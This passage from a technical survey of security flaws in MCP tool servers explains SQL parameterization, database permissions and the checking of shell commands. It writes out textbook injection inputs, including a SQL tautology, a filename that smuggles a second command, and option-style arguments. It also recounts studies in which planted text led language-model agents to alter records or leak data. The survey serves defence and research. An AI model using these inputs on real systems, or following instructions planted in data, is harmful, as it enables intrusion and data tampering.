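| Oliveira and Fiser | 2,287 reports from about 19,000 repositories | a report that human reviewers judged exploitable | 93 flaws, 4.1% of the reports |
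| Padilla | 414 live servers | a flaw in any of nine classes, checked by hand | 68 advisories, 16 per 100 servers |
| *ToFu* | 273 repositories | a verified security or correctness bug in a tool | 118 affected servers, 43% |

*Same Name, Different Server* (2026) summarizes two earlier studies whose results fall between these extremes. One reported general vulnerabilities in 7.2% of 1,899 servers, and the other identified 833 vulnerable servers among 67,057 registry entries. No single percentage can therefore describe how often tools turn arguments into code by mistake. The strictest test, which requires a model to trigger a new flaw with a visible effect, gives a rate of a fraction of one per cent, but it misses many flaws.

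### Why the headline percentages are higher

Security vendors' headline figures are often far above the confirmed counts, partly because producing a scanner alarm takes much less work than confirming a flaw. Trend Micro's first pass produced nearly one alarm per repository. Sun and colleagues tested two existing scanners on 130 servers in which experts had found none of the three classes of flaw. Cisco's scanner flagged 32 of them as vulnerable, and the research tool MCPSafetyScanner flagged 56. Sun and colleagues were comparing these scanners with their own program, but their explanation is plausible. Cisco's scanner relied on tools' descriptions, so a tool that legitimately runs commands or reads files could look unsafe. It also missed 95 of another 130 servers that had real flaws, because a description does not show how the code handles an argument.

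Other percentages measure access control rather than injection. Padilla reports that 91.8% of the servers he tested lacked OAuth, a standard way of granting a program limited access to an account. Some of those servers used other credentials, so they were not all open to everyone. In his third round of measurements, 106 of 464 servers (23%) let anyone call their tools without a credential.

He also counted 687 tools that offered to run shell commands without authentication. These are alarming, but they take program arguments, which are meant to be run.

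Strict counts can also be too low. Oliveira and Fiser set aside 56% of the 438 reports as irrelevant in context, some because they concerned servers on a user's own computer, where an attacker with direct access would already have better ways to attack. That reasoning assumes the caller is trustworthy, but the caller here is a model that may have just read a stranger's e-mail. Oliveira and Fiser acknowledge a similar danger, in which an attacker diverts the connection between the user's computer and the model. They also note that 17% of the reports they set aside involved remote code execution.

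### What developers report and repair

Public reports are better evidence of what kinds of mistake occur than of how often they occur. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* collected 53 reported vulnerabilities in 45 servers. Of these, 43 were "taint-style", meaning that untrusted input flows into a sensitive operation. Command injection accounted for 27, path traversal (a path that leads outside the permitted folder) for nine and SQL injection for two. Trend Micro's figure for SQL injection was much higher, at 26%, which suggests that the mix depends heavily on where researchers look.

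Two studies that searched CVE records up to February 2026 reached different counts of vulnerabilities in MCP servers. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) counts 24 genuine MCP vulnerabilities, 11 of them in servers, and attributes 18 of the 24 to insufficient input validation. The other study counts 35 in open-source servers alone. Researchers in both studies had to decide by hand which records belonged, partly because "MCP" also abbreviates unrelated things.

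Repairs were larger than the textbook remedies suggest. The average fix changed 204 lines of code in three files and took developers 37 days. Four of the 41 repaired flaws remained exploitable. In one server that fetched web pages, the developer added a filter against private network addresses, but a user later pointed out that the filter had the same weaknesses as the code it was based on.

Anthropic's Git server had two of these common faults. The server gives a model tools for running Git, a program that tracks changes to code. He and colleagues list three critical vulnerabilities in the server and describe two, both of which Anthropic fixed in version 2025.12.17.

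In the first, the tools `git_diff` and `git_checkout` passed string arguments to Git without checking them. Command-line programs usually read a word that begins with a hyphen as an option, so a value meant to name a version of the code could change what Git did. This is argument injection. It can happen without a shell because Git itself interprets each word as a name or an option, although He and colleagues classify the case as command injection and illustrate it with text for a shell.

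In the second, whoever set up the server could restrict it to one repository, but the server did not properly check the `repo_path` argument against that restriction, so a path could lead to a different repository. He and colleagues conclude that a check must examine the same normalized path that the tool will later use.

Both arguments were valid strings, and an attacker needed only to influence what the model wrote, for instance through a file it was reading. A pattern in the schema could have rejected names that begin with a hyphen, but no schema could have checked whether a path was inside the permitted repository, because that depends on the server's settings and file system.

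### Can a warning in the tool's description help?

The Tongji University researchers who collected the 53 vulnerabilities also tested a defence for unpatched servers. Their program, SpellSmith, reads a tool's name, description and schema and estimates which arguments could be dangerous. It then rewrites the description to tell the model which operation is sensitive, which arguments outsiders might influence, which types of flaw are likely and which requests to refuse. SpellSmith can also prompt the model to reconsider each call before making it.

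They wrote 792 malicious prompts based on the real vulnerabilities and gave them to GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. Converted from percentages into numbers of prompts that succeeded at least once, the results were:

| Description that the model received | Without reconsidering | After reconsidering |
|---|---|---|
| original | 506 | 25 |
| with a general warning | 225 | 12 |
| with a warning about the wrong type of flaw | 101 | 4 |
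| rewritten by SpellSmith | 72 | 1 |

A warning about the wrong type of flaw worked nearly as well as the correct one, so much of the benefit seems to come from making the model more cautious, and less from telling it what to look for. The warnings may also make the model refuse legitimate calls. The benchmark doesn't measure this because it contains only malicious prompts, and a model that refused everything would have scored perfectly.

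The prompts were also fixed in advance, whereas VIPER-MCP succeeded by revising a request after each failure. A defence that depends on the model's judgement has to withstand such repeated attempts. A description can still be a useful extra layer when a developer cannot change a server's code, but it does not fix the handler, so a legitimate request for O'Brien's invoices will still fail.

### Who must validate a start-up command?

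When a client uses an MCP server on the same computer, it starts the server as a child process with a command from its configuration, so that string is run as code before the model has called any tool. The process has the same access to files as the user. The client can't find out whether the program is an MCP server until it has run the command.

In 2026 the security company OX Security and Anthropic disagreed about who should validate that command. MCP's official software kits pass the command on for execution. OX Security considers this a design flaw that puts every application built on the kits at risk, and it wants Anthropic to add protection to the kits. Anthropic considers it intended behaviour to start the configured command, and leaves validation to the developers of applications that accept the configuration.

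Anthropic's position has a sound technical basis. A software kit receives the start-up command as an argument and cannot tell whether the user or a stranger supplied it. An allowlist of program names would not help much, because developers commonly distribute local servers through package runners such as npx and uvx. These download and run whatever package the command names, so allowing npx would let almost anything run.

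The case for OX Security's position is that application developers keep making the same mistake. Reported examples include a vulnerability in the client Dive, where a link could install a server without sufficient confirmation from the user, and inadequate control over command execution in the chat application LibreChat and the agent builder Flowise. Gaps in the early MCP specification may have left room for unsafe defaults. Padilla makes a similar argument about authentication, recalling that the databases Elasticsearch and Redis once shipped open to the network and needed repair on a large scale. He argues that protection developers must remember to switch on is not enough.

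The two positions are partly compatible. Only the application can determine where a configuration came from, so only the application can decide whether to trust it. The software kit could still refuse to start a new command until the application confirms that a person has seen and approved it, which is close to the remedy that He and colleagues recommend for Dive. A user could still approve a harmful command, but developers could no longer skip the decision by accident.

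## What do parameterized queries protect, and what do they leave open?

OX Security and Anthropic disagreed about who should check a string before an interpreter runs it. Nobody has to make that check on a customer's name if the handler uses a parameterized query.

PostgreSQL's *Overview*, a page in the manual of the open-source database PostgreSQL, describes two ways to send a query. In the simple protocol, the client sends one string, which the database parses and runs at once. The extended protocol has three steps. In the first, usually called "prepare", the database parses the query text and keeps the result as a prepared statement, which may still lack values. It then binds values to the statement, and finally it executes it. If `find_invoices` always sorts by due date, a search for Ms O'Brien's invoices looks like this:

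| Step | What the handler sends | What the database does |
|---|---|---|
| Prepare | `SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = $1 ORDER BY due_date` | parses the text, looks up the table and columns, and keeps the prepared statement |
| Bind | `O'Brien` | attaches these seven characters to `$1` |
| Execute | a request to run the bound statement | returns the invoices whose customer equals those seven characters |

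After the first step the condition already has its final parse tree:

```
condition
└─ comparison
   ├─ column: customer
   ├─ =
   └─ parameter $1 (text)
```

PostgreSQL parses a parameterized query before it receives any values. Hackeriet's *Simple and Extended queries in PostgreSQL* lists the fields of the first message as a name for the statement, the query text, the number of parameters and their types, with no field for a value. The database does not run its SQL parser again when the value arrives, so an apostrophe in the value cannot close a string. If the parameter is a name, PostgreSQL treats the textbook input `' OR '1'='1` as an unusual name, and the input fills exactly one node under Su and Wassermann's parse-tree definition.

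The database still converts each value to the type of its parameter. The conversion function follows the data type's rules, not SQL's grammar, so it rejects `7 OR 1=1` when `$1` is a numeric parameter.

### Placeholders that the client fills in

Two calls in a Python handler can look almost alike:

```python
cur.execute(f"SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = '{customer}'")
cur.execute("SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = %s", (customer,))
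```

The first pastes the name into the query. The second passes the query text and the name separately to the driver, the library that connects the program to the database. According to Go's documentation, its SQL package then prepares the statement and sends the parameter separately. Other drivers escape the value themselves, put it where the placeholder was, and send the database a single string. Educative's *PostgreSQL Protocol* notes that PostgreSQL has had a function for sending query text and values separately since 2003, and that many drivers still don't offer it.

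Escaping by a well-maintained driver handles O'Brien and the textbook input correctly, and it is far safer than escaping by hand. The manual for Psycopg, a Python driver, warns developers never to merge values into a query themselves. But a driver that escapes has to follow the same quoting rules as the database, which brings back the problem of two parsers. Numbers can also cause errors. If a query contains `credit -$1` and the driver pastes in the value -5, the result is `credit --5`. Two hyphens begin a comment in SQL, so the database ignores the rest of the line. This doesn't happen when the database does the binding, because it has parsed the minus sign before the number arrives.

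### Names, wildcards, old text and the wrong customer

A parameter can be used only where SQL allows a value. `SELECT * FROM $1` is a syntax error, because the database needs the table name to prepare the query. Passing the `sort_by` argument as a parameter fails without an error. PostgreSQL accepts `ORDER BY $1`, but if the value is `due_date`, it sorts by that string instead of by the column. The string is the same for every row, so the invoices come back in no particular order.

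The usual remedy is to let the argument select a piece of SQL that the developer wrote:

```python
SORT_KEYS = {
    "due_date": "due_date ASC",
    "newest":   "due_date DESC",
    "amount":   "amount DESC",
}
query = ("SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = %s ORDER BY "
         + SORT_KEYS[sort_by])
```

An unknown key causes an error, and no text from the model reaches the query. If the developer cannot list the names in advance, such as when users create their own tables, the handler can quote the name as an identifier, preferably with a function from the driver. Quoting ensures that the database reads the text as one name, but it may still be the wrong name. For example, a user who is not allowed to see customers' credit scores could learn how the customers rank by sorting on that column.

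A bound value can still contain wildcards that the database interprets. Suppose `find_invoices` accepts part of a customer's name and its query uses `customer LIKE $1`. In a LIKE pattern, `%` matches any text and `_` matches any single character, so the value `%` returns every customer's invoices even though the binding worked correctly. An underscore can also match by accident. For example, `O_Brien`, the name as CERT's sample code altered it, would find O'Brien. The handler can escape the two wildcards before binding or use a function that searches for plain text, such as PostgreSQL's `starts_with`. An empty string still matches everything in either kind of search, so the tool also needs a minimum length or a limit on rows.

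Binding, like escaping, protects only the query in which it happens. If a program later pastes stored text into a new query, a second-order attack is still possible. For example, if `find_invoices` saves recent searches so that a user can repeat one, the handler that repeats the search has to bind the stored name again. The same applies to every query that uses values from the firm's own tables.

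A correctly bound value can also name the wrong customer. A prompt injection in a supplier's e-mail might lead the model to call `find_invoices` for one of that supplier's competitors. Web developers have long called this flaw an insecure direct object reference, in which a program returns whatever record a request names without checking that the requester may see it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian document a version of the attack that passes through a language model. The handler can prevent it by adding a second condition to the query, such as `AND account_manager = $2`, if it takes the second value from the user's login session and never from the model's arguments. Genkit's *MCP Toolbox for Databases* describes a ready-made MCP server that can restrict access to a tool according to who has logged in, but the second condition is still needed to limit whose invoices `find_invoices` returns.

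### Bound parameters and templates in tool servers

The same Toolbox lets a developer define a tool by writing its SQL in a configuration file. According to Google's *postgres-sql*, the manual page for its PostgreSQL tools, such a tool can have two lists of arguments. Those under `parameters` are for values, while those under `templateParameters` go into the text of the statement before the database prepares it, so they can supply a table name. The page's example statement is `SELECT * FROM {{.tableName}}`, which is still in the version for release 1.1.0, from April 2026.

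The two lists show a human reader which arguments can change the structure of the query. The declared type doesn't show this, since `tableName` is a "string" in the example, just as a customer's name would be. A developer who uses a template argument therefore needs a short list of permitted names, as with `sort_by`. If there are only three tables, three separate tools with fixed queries would also work.

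Some servers have the model write the query as well as supply the values. Glama's *execute_sql*, an entry in a directory of MCP servers, describes a tool that takes SQL text and a list of parameters, and instructs the model to use placeholders to prevent injection. This helps with honest mistakes, because if the model puts O'Brien in the list, the apostrophe cannot break the query. It does little against prompt injection, because binding works only when the programmer fixes the query text before any untrusted value arrives. Here the model writes that text, so an injected prompt can mislead it into writing a harmful query.

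### Query text as a type

A developer who uses placeholders in most queries may still paste a string directly into another. Several programming languages now let a library author require that query text come from the program's source code, so that a type checker catches this mistake.

Google's `safesql` library for Go does this with a small trick. Its function for creating a query takes a type that code outside the library cannot name:

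```go
type stringConstant string
func New(text stringConstant) TrustedSQLString
```

Go automatically converts a constant in the source code to the private type that `New` accepts. A string received at runtime needs an explicit conversion, which code outside the library can't write because it can't name the type. The compiler therefore accepts `New("SELECT ...")` and rejects `New(sql)` if `sql` came from a tool call. The library's query functions accept only the `TrustedSQLString` that `New` returns. Google uses a similar approach in Java, where a separate checker requires the text to be a constant.

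Python acquired a comparable type, `LiteralString`, in version 3.11. PEP 675, the design document that introduced it, uses SQL injection as its main example. A type checker gives this type to text written in the program and to combinations of such texts:

```python
def run(sql: LiteralString, params: tuple) -> list: ...

run("SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = %s", (customer,))    # accepted
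run(f"SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = '{customer}'", ())  # rejected
```

The argument `customer` has the ordinary type `str`, so any string that contains it also has that type. The table of sort keys passes the check if the developer declares its entries as `LiteralString`, because the model chooses among strings that the programmer wrote. Python ignores these types at runtime, so the protection disappears if a team doesn't use a type checker or suppresses its warning.

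PEP 750 added template strings to Python 3.14. The expression `t"... WHERE customer = {customer}"` looks like the dangerous version above, with a `t` in place of the `f`, but it produces an object that stores the programmer's text and the inserted values separately. A driver that accepts these objects can turn the text into a query with placeholders and bind the values, so the most convenient way to write the query also becomes a safe one. Each driver has to do this correctly, since the object has no built-in handling for SQL.

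The evidence that such types reduce injection comes mostly from Google's accounts of its own code. Google introduced the types together with compulsory checks and reviews, so their separate effect is uncertain. The types also don't guarantee that a query is correct, since a programmer can write a constant query that returns everybody's invoices. And they cannot accept the SQL passed to `run_query(sql)`, because the model writes it. To run that SQL, the developer has to bypass the type explicitly, which at least shows a reviewer where to look.

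### When the argument is the query

Parameterized queries help little with `run_query`, because the model writes the whole query and there are no separate values left to bind. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of systems that translate questions into SQL, lists parameterized queries among its countermeasures to injection, along with read-only execution and checks on the output. For tools like `run_query`, protection has to come mostly from the last two.

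In *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023) were the first to study what they call prompt-to-SQL injection. They built a chatbot for a job-advertisement website with OpenAI's GPT-3.5 and LangChain, a library for connecting models to other software. The chatbot's database connection could read and change everything, so the model was the only safeguard. They tried seven attacks, thirty times each, on a version that ran one query per question and on an agent that could run several.

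With LangChain's standard prompt, the chatbot deleted a table, changed a record and listed all users when asked. Pedro and colleagues then added instructions that forbade changes to the data or access to other users' records. These stopped the crudest attempts. When asked for another user's e-mail address, the chatbot once wrote a query requiring the user number to be both 1 and 2, which returned nothing. But slightly more elaborate requests succeeded every time. In two further attacks, the attacker only placed text in a job advertisement, without talking to the chatbot. When an honest user later asked about the advertisements, the chatbot read the text and changed a third person's e-mail address.

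They repeated the restricted attacks on six other models. Two could not run the agent version reliably. Of the other four, GPT-4 was the most robust, and it resisted only the attack that needed several queries. They then tested four defences on a bookshop application: a database login with fewer permissions, a rewrite of each query to cover only the user's own rows, a second model that inspected query results for planted instructions, and a prompt that already contained the user's own data, so that no query was necessary.

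| Attack | Defences that stopped it |
|---|---|
| delete a table on request | fewer permissions |
| change a record on request | fewer permissions |
| list a whole table | rewriting; data in the prompt |
| delete a table although the prompt forbids changes | fewer permissions |
| read another user's record although the prompt forbids it | rewriting; data in the prompt |
| give false answers because of planted text | second model |
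| change an e-mail address because of planted text | fewer permissions; second model |

No single defence stopped every attack. Only the second model caught the false answers, because the query in that attack was the one the honest user needed and the harm was in the text it returned. Pedro and colleagues call this model a partial defence, since prompt injection may work on it too. The tests used the same attacks that the defences were designed for, so they show little about how the defences would handle new ones.

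Later studies suggest that better models have reduced the problem without removing it. *Data Agents Under Attack* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested six systems that answer questions by querying databases, including commercial services from Databricks and Google. One attack planted SQL fragments in stored data so that the model might include them in its next query. It succeeded in none of 25 attempts on Databricks' service and in six of 25 on Google's BigQuery. In one open-source system, its success rate ranged from 24% to 48% across four newer models and was highest with OpenAI's GPT-5.2. Success meant any unauthorized effect, even one confined to a single reply, so these rates don't measure how often data was lost.

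A model can write a forbidden query even when nobody is attacking it. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (Fei and Yang, 2026) gave models ordinary questions and a description of what the user's role was allowed to read. The model had to write a permitted query or refuse. On BIRD, a collection of questions about large real-world databases, Claude Sonnet 4.5 broke the access rules on 7.7% of questions, GPT-5 on 10.5%, and Snowflake-Arctic-R1-7B, a small model specialized in SQL, on 65.1%.

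Not all of these violations would leak data. GPT-5-mini committed about 194 in an average round of 1,534 questions. In 126 of them, it answered a question it should have refused using only permitted columns, so the user would probably have received a wrong answer but no secret. The other 69 or so, about 4.5% of the questions, touched forbidden columns. Leaving those columns out of the description that the model received halved the number that DeepSeek's V3.2 tried to read, but doubled GPT-5-mini's attempts, as it guessed at names it had not been given.

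Other researchers try to control the model's output more directly. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (2025) uses one model to write the SQL and another to check it against the user's permissions. *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (2026) applies the policy while the model is writing, just as strict tool use restricts a call to its schema. Both may increase the share of questions that get a usable answer, but neither justifies giving the database login more rights than the user has. Fei and Yang want enforcement to stay in the database.

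### What the database can refuse

A database role is a named set of permissions, and each connection logs in under one. For the invoicing assistant, the developer might write:

```sql
CREATE ROLE assistant LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT (number, customer, amount, due_date) ON invoices TO assistant;
```

The database checks these permissions on every query, whoever wrote it. A query that deletes invoices fails, and so does one that reads a fifth column. PostgreSQL and many other databases can grant permissions by column, as here, although Pedro and colleagues wrote that permissions apply only to whole tables. One common gap in the guarantee is that some database functions run with their creator's rights, so the assistant's role must not be able to call any that change or reveal more than they should.

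A weaker way to prevent changes is to run each query inside a read-only transaction. Datadog Security Labs describes a PostgreSQL tool server that opens such a transaction, runs the submitted query and then rolls the transaction back. PostgreSQL refuses a command to delete all the tables while the transaction is open. But SQL commands can end the transaction, whereas a missing permission stays missing whatever the query contains. A server that relies on the transaction should at least accept only one statement per call.

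Neither method limits which invoices the assistant can read. For that, PostgreSQL offers row-level security:

```sql
ALTER TABLE invoices ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
CREATE POLICY own_customers ON invoices FOR SELECT
  USING (account_manager = current_user);
```

The database now adds the condition to every query on the table. `SELECT * FROM invoices` returns only the invoices of customers whom the logged-in user manages, and a query for other customers' invoices returns nothing. This also solves the wrong-customer problem in `find_invoices`, even if the developer forgets the second condition there.

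The protection depends on how the assistant logs in. PostgreSQL exempts administrators and, by default, the table's owner, so an assistant that connects as the owner sees every row. Many applications use one login for all users and record the current user in a session setting, which the policy then reads. That can work for `find_invoices`, where the developer wrote the SQL, but it is unsafe for `run_query`, because a query can change the setting. For `run_query`, each user needs a separate login, or the server has to keep the user's identity somewhere that SQL cannot alter.

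A restricted view, which is a stored query that users can treat as a table, gives a similar result. The developer can define `my_invoices` as four columns of `invoices` with the same condition on `account_manager`, and give the assistant permission to read the view but not the table. Pedro and colleagues' rewriting defence imitates this, but it relies on their own Python parser to recognize every mention of the table, whereas the database itself enforces the restrictions of a view. In PostgreSQL, a view that hides rows should carry the option `security_barrier`. Without it, the database may apply a function from the user's query to hidden rows before filtering them out.

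### Checking the parsed query

A checker can also parse the model's SQL before the database receives it. Fei and Yang express the basic test in one line. Let Perm(*q*) be the set of combinations of table, column and operation that the query *q* uses, and Π<sub>*r*</sub> the set that the role *r* may use. The query is allowed if

Perm(*q*) ⊆ Π<sub>*r*</sub>

They extract the first set with SQLGlot, a SQL parser. For `SELECT amount FROM invoices WHERE customer = 'Acme'`, the set contains reads of `amount` and `customer`, since columns used in conditions also count.

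If the checker parses SQL exactly as the database does and correctly identifies what each name stands for, the test guarantees that the query text refers only to items on the list. An asterisk stands for every column, a view may read several tables, and a function call may do almost anything. A cautious checker therefore rejects any function or construction it doesn't recognize.

Many tools use a simpler test. *AgentNLQ* (2026) describes a question-answering system that refuses nine kinds of statement, including insert, update, delete and drop. This is a blocklist, with the weakness that Andersen and Cohen noticed in 1996. A checker that accepts only SELECT has a shorter rule and doesn't have to predict which other statements to refuse. Glama's *execute-query* entry describes a server that blocks several kinds of statement and requires a WHERE condition on updates and deletions. That catches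 a forgotten condition, but not one that covers too many rows. The entry's description lists insertions as supported, but its summary of the code lists them as blocked, so a model that relies on the description may waste calls on them.

A parser can enforce rules that permissions do not express, such as a maximum number of joined tables, but it cannot replace permissions. It can also return the reason for refusing a query, so that the model can write a better one. Fei and Yang point out that a bare refusal by the database is safe but leaves the user without an answer.

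All these controls check one query at a time. A user who may read hourly wages and hours worked can calculate a salary without permission to read the salary column. Fei and Yang leave such inferences out of their benchmark. Wang and colleagues tested attacks that combine several permitted queries to reconstruct protected records. On BigQuery, three of 25 attacks succeeded when the attacker chose the queries, and three of 25 when the agent planned them. Possible remedies are to refuse totals that cover too few people, limit the number of queries, or add random noise to the results, but each makes the answers less useful to honest users.

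Query results can also carry instructions back to the model, as the planted job advertisements did. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) proposes that the model write the query but never receive the result, and that ordinary software show it to the user. The model then cannot check whether the data answers the question or use the first result to write a second query.

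Finally, a permitted query can take too long. In one of Wang and colleagues' tests, an agent tried to combine every row of one 13.8-million-row table with every row of another the same size, and did not respond for thirty minutes because the software had no way to cancel a running query. PostgreSQL has a time limit for statements, but it is another session setting that a query can change. The server that calls the database for `run_query` should therefore time the query itself and cancel it at a set limit.

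## Can a shell command be checked before it runs?

A database can check a query from `run_query` against a list of permissions before running it, but a shell has no such list. It starts the programs that a command names, and those programs can do whatever the operating system allows their account to do. To refuse some of the commands that reach `run_command`, a developer therefore needs a checker that can tell from a command's text what it will do.

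### From a line of text to a running program

Suppose the model wants to count the lines in every exported report and save the counts:

```sh
wc -l $REPORTS/*.csv > "counts $(date +%F).txt"
```

Here `wc -l` counts lines, `$REPORTS` stands for the value of a variable, `*` matches any text in a file name, `>` sends the output to a file, and `$(...)` stands for the output of another command. POSIX (The Open Group, 2024), the standard that most Unix shells broadly follow, specifies the order in which a shell processes such a line.

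| Step | What happens to this line |
|---|---|
| Splitting | The shell breaks the text into `wc`, `-l`, `$REPORTS/*.csv`, `>` and the quoted file name. |
| Parsing | It recognizes one command with two arguments and one redirection. |
| Expansion | It replaces `$REPORTS` with its value, say `/srv/reports`, and the pattern with the names of matching files. |
| Redirection | It runs `date` to complete the name of the output file, then creates the file or empties an existing one. |
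| Execution | It looks for a program called `wc` and starts it with the resulting arguments. |

When the shell expands a command, it fills in home folders, variables, command output and arithmetic, then splits the results at spaces, looks for matching file names, and finally removes the quotation marks. Before these steps, Bash also performs brace expansion, which turns `{a,b}` into two words, according to *3.5 Shell Expansions* in GNU's Bash manual.

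Because the shell looks for semicolons before it fills in variables, a semicolon in the value of `REPORTS` does not start a new command. A space, however, can split the value. If it is `/srv/march reports`, `wc` receives the two arguments `/srv/march` and `reports/*.csv`, assuming the pattern matches nothing. If the variable is empty, the shell looks for reports at the top of the file system. *Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell* (Greenberg and Blatt, 2019) mentions a script for the games service Steam that wiped users' hard drives because of a misunderstanding about expansion. A variable that should have contained Steam's folder was empty, so a command to delete everything in that folder started at the top of the file system.

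Command substitution, written `$(...)`, runs a program while the shell is still preparing the command line. A command that begins with `echo`, which only prints text, can therefore run any number of other programs before `echo` starts. Redirection also happens before the main program runs, so if `wc` fails in `wc -l data.txt > counts.txt`, the old contents of `counts.txt` are already gone.

So the line's effect depends on the value of `REPORTS`, the files in a folder, the date, and the variable `PATH`, which lists the folders where the shell looks for programs. None of this is in the string. A checker can look it up, but another program may change it before the shell runs the line.

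Greenberg and Blatt wrote a complete definition of the shell's behaviour as a program called Smoosh, which can run commands on the real operating system or simulate one and show each step of the expansion. The definition takes the state of the operating system as an input, because ordinary shell operations such as opening files and starting processes depend on it. They counted 70 relevant uses of "unspecified" and 17 of "undefined" in the standard, which leave some behaviour open. They also found bugs in four shells in active use, in the standard and in its test suite. A checker that follows the standard exactly may therefore still parse a command differently from the shell that runs it.

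A perfect model of the shell would still not cover the programs it starts. In *From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again*, Lazarek, Jung and colleagues (2025) write that even careful developers discover serious bugs only when a script runs, partly because these programs are opaque and the shell interacts with its environment in complex ways. Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues add in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects* that a shell program's effects are often irreversible.

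### Starting the converter without a shell

The `convert_report` tool avoids most of these difficulties because its filename is a value argument and the developer already knows which program to run. Suppose the program is `report2pdf`. A handler in Python can start it in two ways:

```python
subprocess.run(f"report2pdf {filename}", shell=True)
subprocess.run(["report2pdf", filename])
```

The first line builds a command and passes it to a shell, so the apostrophe in `O'Brien.docx` causes an error. With the textbook input `march.docx; echo hello`, the line converts the March report and then runs a second command.

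The second line doesn't use a shell. Python starts `report2pdf` through the operating system and passes the arguments as a list of separate strings. On Unix, the operating system copies these strings to the new program without parsing them, so spaces, semicolons and apostrophes are ordinary characters. `report2pdf` looks for a file named `march.docx; echo hello` and doesn't find it. Passing a list is like using a parameterized query in SQL, because the filename is never part of the text that is parsed as a command.

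MITRE's *CWE-88*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, recommends passing arguments separately wherever possible and rates the method's effectiveness as high. It also mentions functions that escape a single argument for the shell. As with SQL, an escaping function has to follow the rules of the interpreter that reads the result.

Sometimes a handler needs a feature of the shell, such as a pipe, which sends one program's output to another. The developer can then write a fixed command and pass the filename separately:

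```python
subprocess.run(["sh", "-c", 'report2pdf "$1" | gzip > out.gz',
                "sh", filename])
```

The shell parses the fixed text before it replaces `$1` with the filename, and the double quotation marks keep a name with spaces in one piece. The second `"sh"` only gives the shell a name to use in error messages. This is safe because the developer wrote the whole command string that follows `-c`. If a handler pastes the filename into that string, the shell can read parts of the name as commands, even though the arguments are passed as a list.

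Starting a program directly also means that no shell expands patterns, so the filename `*.docx` refers to a single file with an asterisk in its name. The developer of a single-file tool probably wants this. Some programs still pass their arguments to a shell. The remote-login program `ssh`, for example, joins the words of a remote command into one string, which a shell on the other computer parses. On Windows, the operating system gives a new program a single command line to split, so whether it receives the intended arguments depends partly on the program.

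### File names that look like options

Passing arguments as a list keeps them separate but doesn't mark which ones are options, so argument injection is still possible. Anthropic's Git server had this flaw because Git could read a version name that began with a hyphen as an option.

MITRE gives the example of a small program that lists a file's details with `ls -l`. The program accepts only names made of letters, digits, underscores and hyphens, which excludes every character that could start a new shell command or lead to another folder. But `-aR` also passes this check, and `ls` treats it as options instead of a file name, so it lists the current folder and all the folders inside it.

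Spaces can have a similar effect if the handler builds a command as a single string. MITRE describes a mail library that validated the sender's address before adding it to a command. Valid e-mail addresses can contain spaces, so an address could pass the check and still add extra options for the mail program. An argument list would have kept the address in one piece, but the program could still read a value that begins with a hyphen as an option.

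These flaws are common. GCVE's *CWE-88*, a page in a public vulnerability database, lists 762 vulnerabilities of this type, including some duplicates. One duplicate is an August 2026 report about a Python library that passed options to Git unchecked. The database later withdrew the report because another entry already covered the flaw.

There are several defences, and a developer can combine them:

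- Many programs treat everything after a bare `--` as data, so a handler can run `["report2pdf", "--", filename]`. This is only a convention, and the developer has to confirm that the program follows it. In Git, `--` separates versions from file names, so it doesn't protect an argument that names a version. Newer releases of Git have a separate marker, `--end-of-options`, for that purpose.
- If the argument is a file in the current folder, the handler can put `./` in front of its name. `./-aR` refers to the same file as `-aR` but doesn't begin with a hyphen. This also deals with a name that consists of a single hyphen, which many programs take to mean their standard input.
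- The handler can require the first character to be a letter or digit. MITRE's corrected pattern is close to this, although it also accepts an underscore and, by accident, rejects names of only one character.
- The handler can copy the report to a file whose name it has chosen, such as `input.docx`, and convert that. The program then never receives any text from the model as an argument.
- A library function can sometimes replace the program. MITRE suggests this for the listing example, since a programming language can read a file's details without starting `ls`.

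These ensure that `report2pdf` treats the filename as the name of a file, but they don't prevent the model from choosing the wrong report or a path that leads out of the reports folder.

### Why a list of permitted programs is weak

The whole string passed to `run_command` is a program, so there is no separate value to pass. Developers often check it against an allowlist of program names. The checker splits the command into its parts, finds the program in each, and approves the command if every program is on the list. A list for looking through files might contain `ls`, `grep`, `sort` and `find`.

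Some programs with harmless-sounding names can change files or run other programs. `sort` has an option that writes its result to a file, and `find` can delete the files it finds or start another program for each one. `awk`, which many people use to pick columns out of a table, is a full programming language. Developers' tools such as `make` and `npm` run instructions stored in the project's files, so approving `npm test` means approving whatever those files contain. Even a program that only prints text can destroy a file if the shell redirects its output to that file.

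A command name does not always identify the program that will run. If the name contains no slash, a shell may run a built-in command, a previously defined function, or the first matching program it finds through `PATH`. An attacker who can change `PATH` or put a file in one of its folders may be able to run their own program in place of a permitted one.

*ParseGap* (Li, November 2026), a single-author preprint, found that the checkers of all eight coding agents it tested approved some commands whose effects broke the policy.

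### ShellPlan: running the plan that was checked

The same preprint proposes a remedy, ShellPlan, which parses each command once into a structured plan, checks the plan, and carries out approved plans itself, without a shell. Because ShellPlan uses only one parser, a difference between the checker's parser and the shell's can no longer let a command through.

ShellPlan accepts only part of Bash's language. A plan has one of these forms:

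```
plan  =   command
     or   plan ;  plan     run one, then the other
     or   plan && plan     run the second if the first succeeds
     or   plan || plan     run the second if the first fails
     or   plan |  plan     send the output of one to the other
```

In ShellPlan, each command consists of variable assignments, a program name, arguments and redirections. The arguments may contain variables, file patterns and command substitutions, which contain smaller plans. The program name must appear literally, so a variable cannot supply it. The language has no loops. ShellPlan rejects any command outside these rules or refers it to a person.

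ShellPlan then compares each program's arguments with a specification for that program. Specifications exist for 20 utilities, including `grep`, `sort`, `find` and a few read-only Git operations. They list the options and arguments that ShellPlan accepts and exclude the rest, so the specification for `sort` leaves out the option that writes to a file. If Σ<sub>*b*</sub> is the set of argument lists that the specification for program *b* allows, the test is

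arguments of *b* ∈ Σ<sub>*b*</sub>

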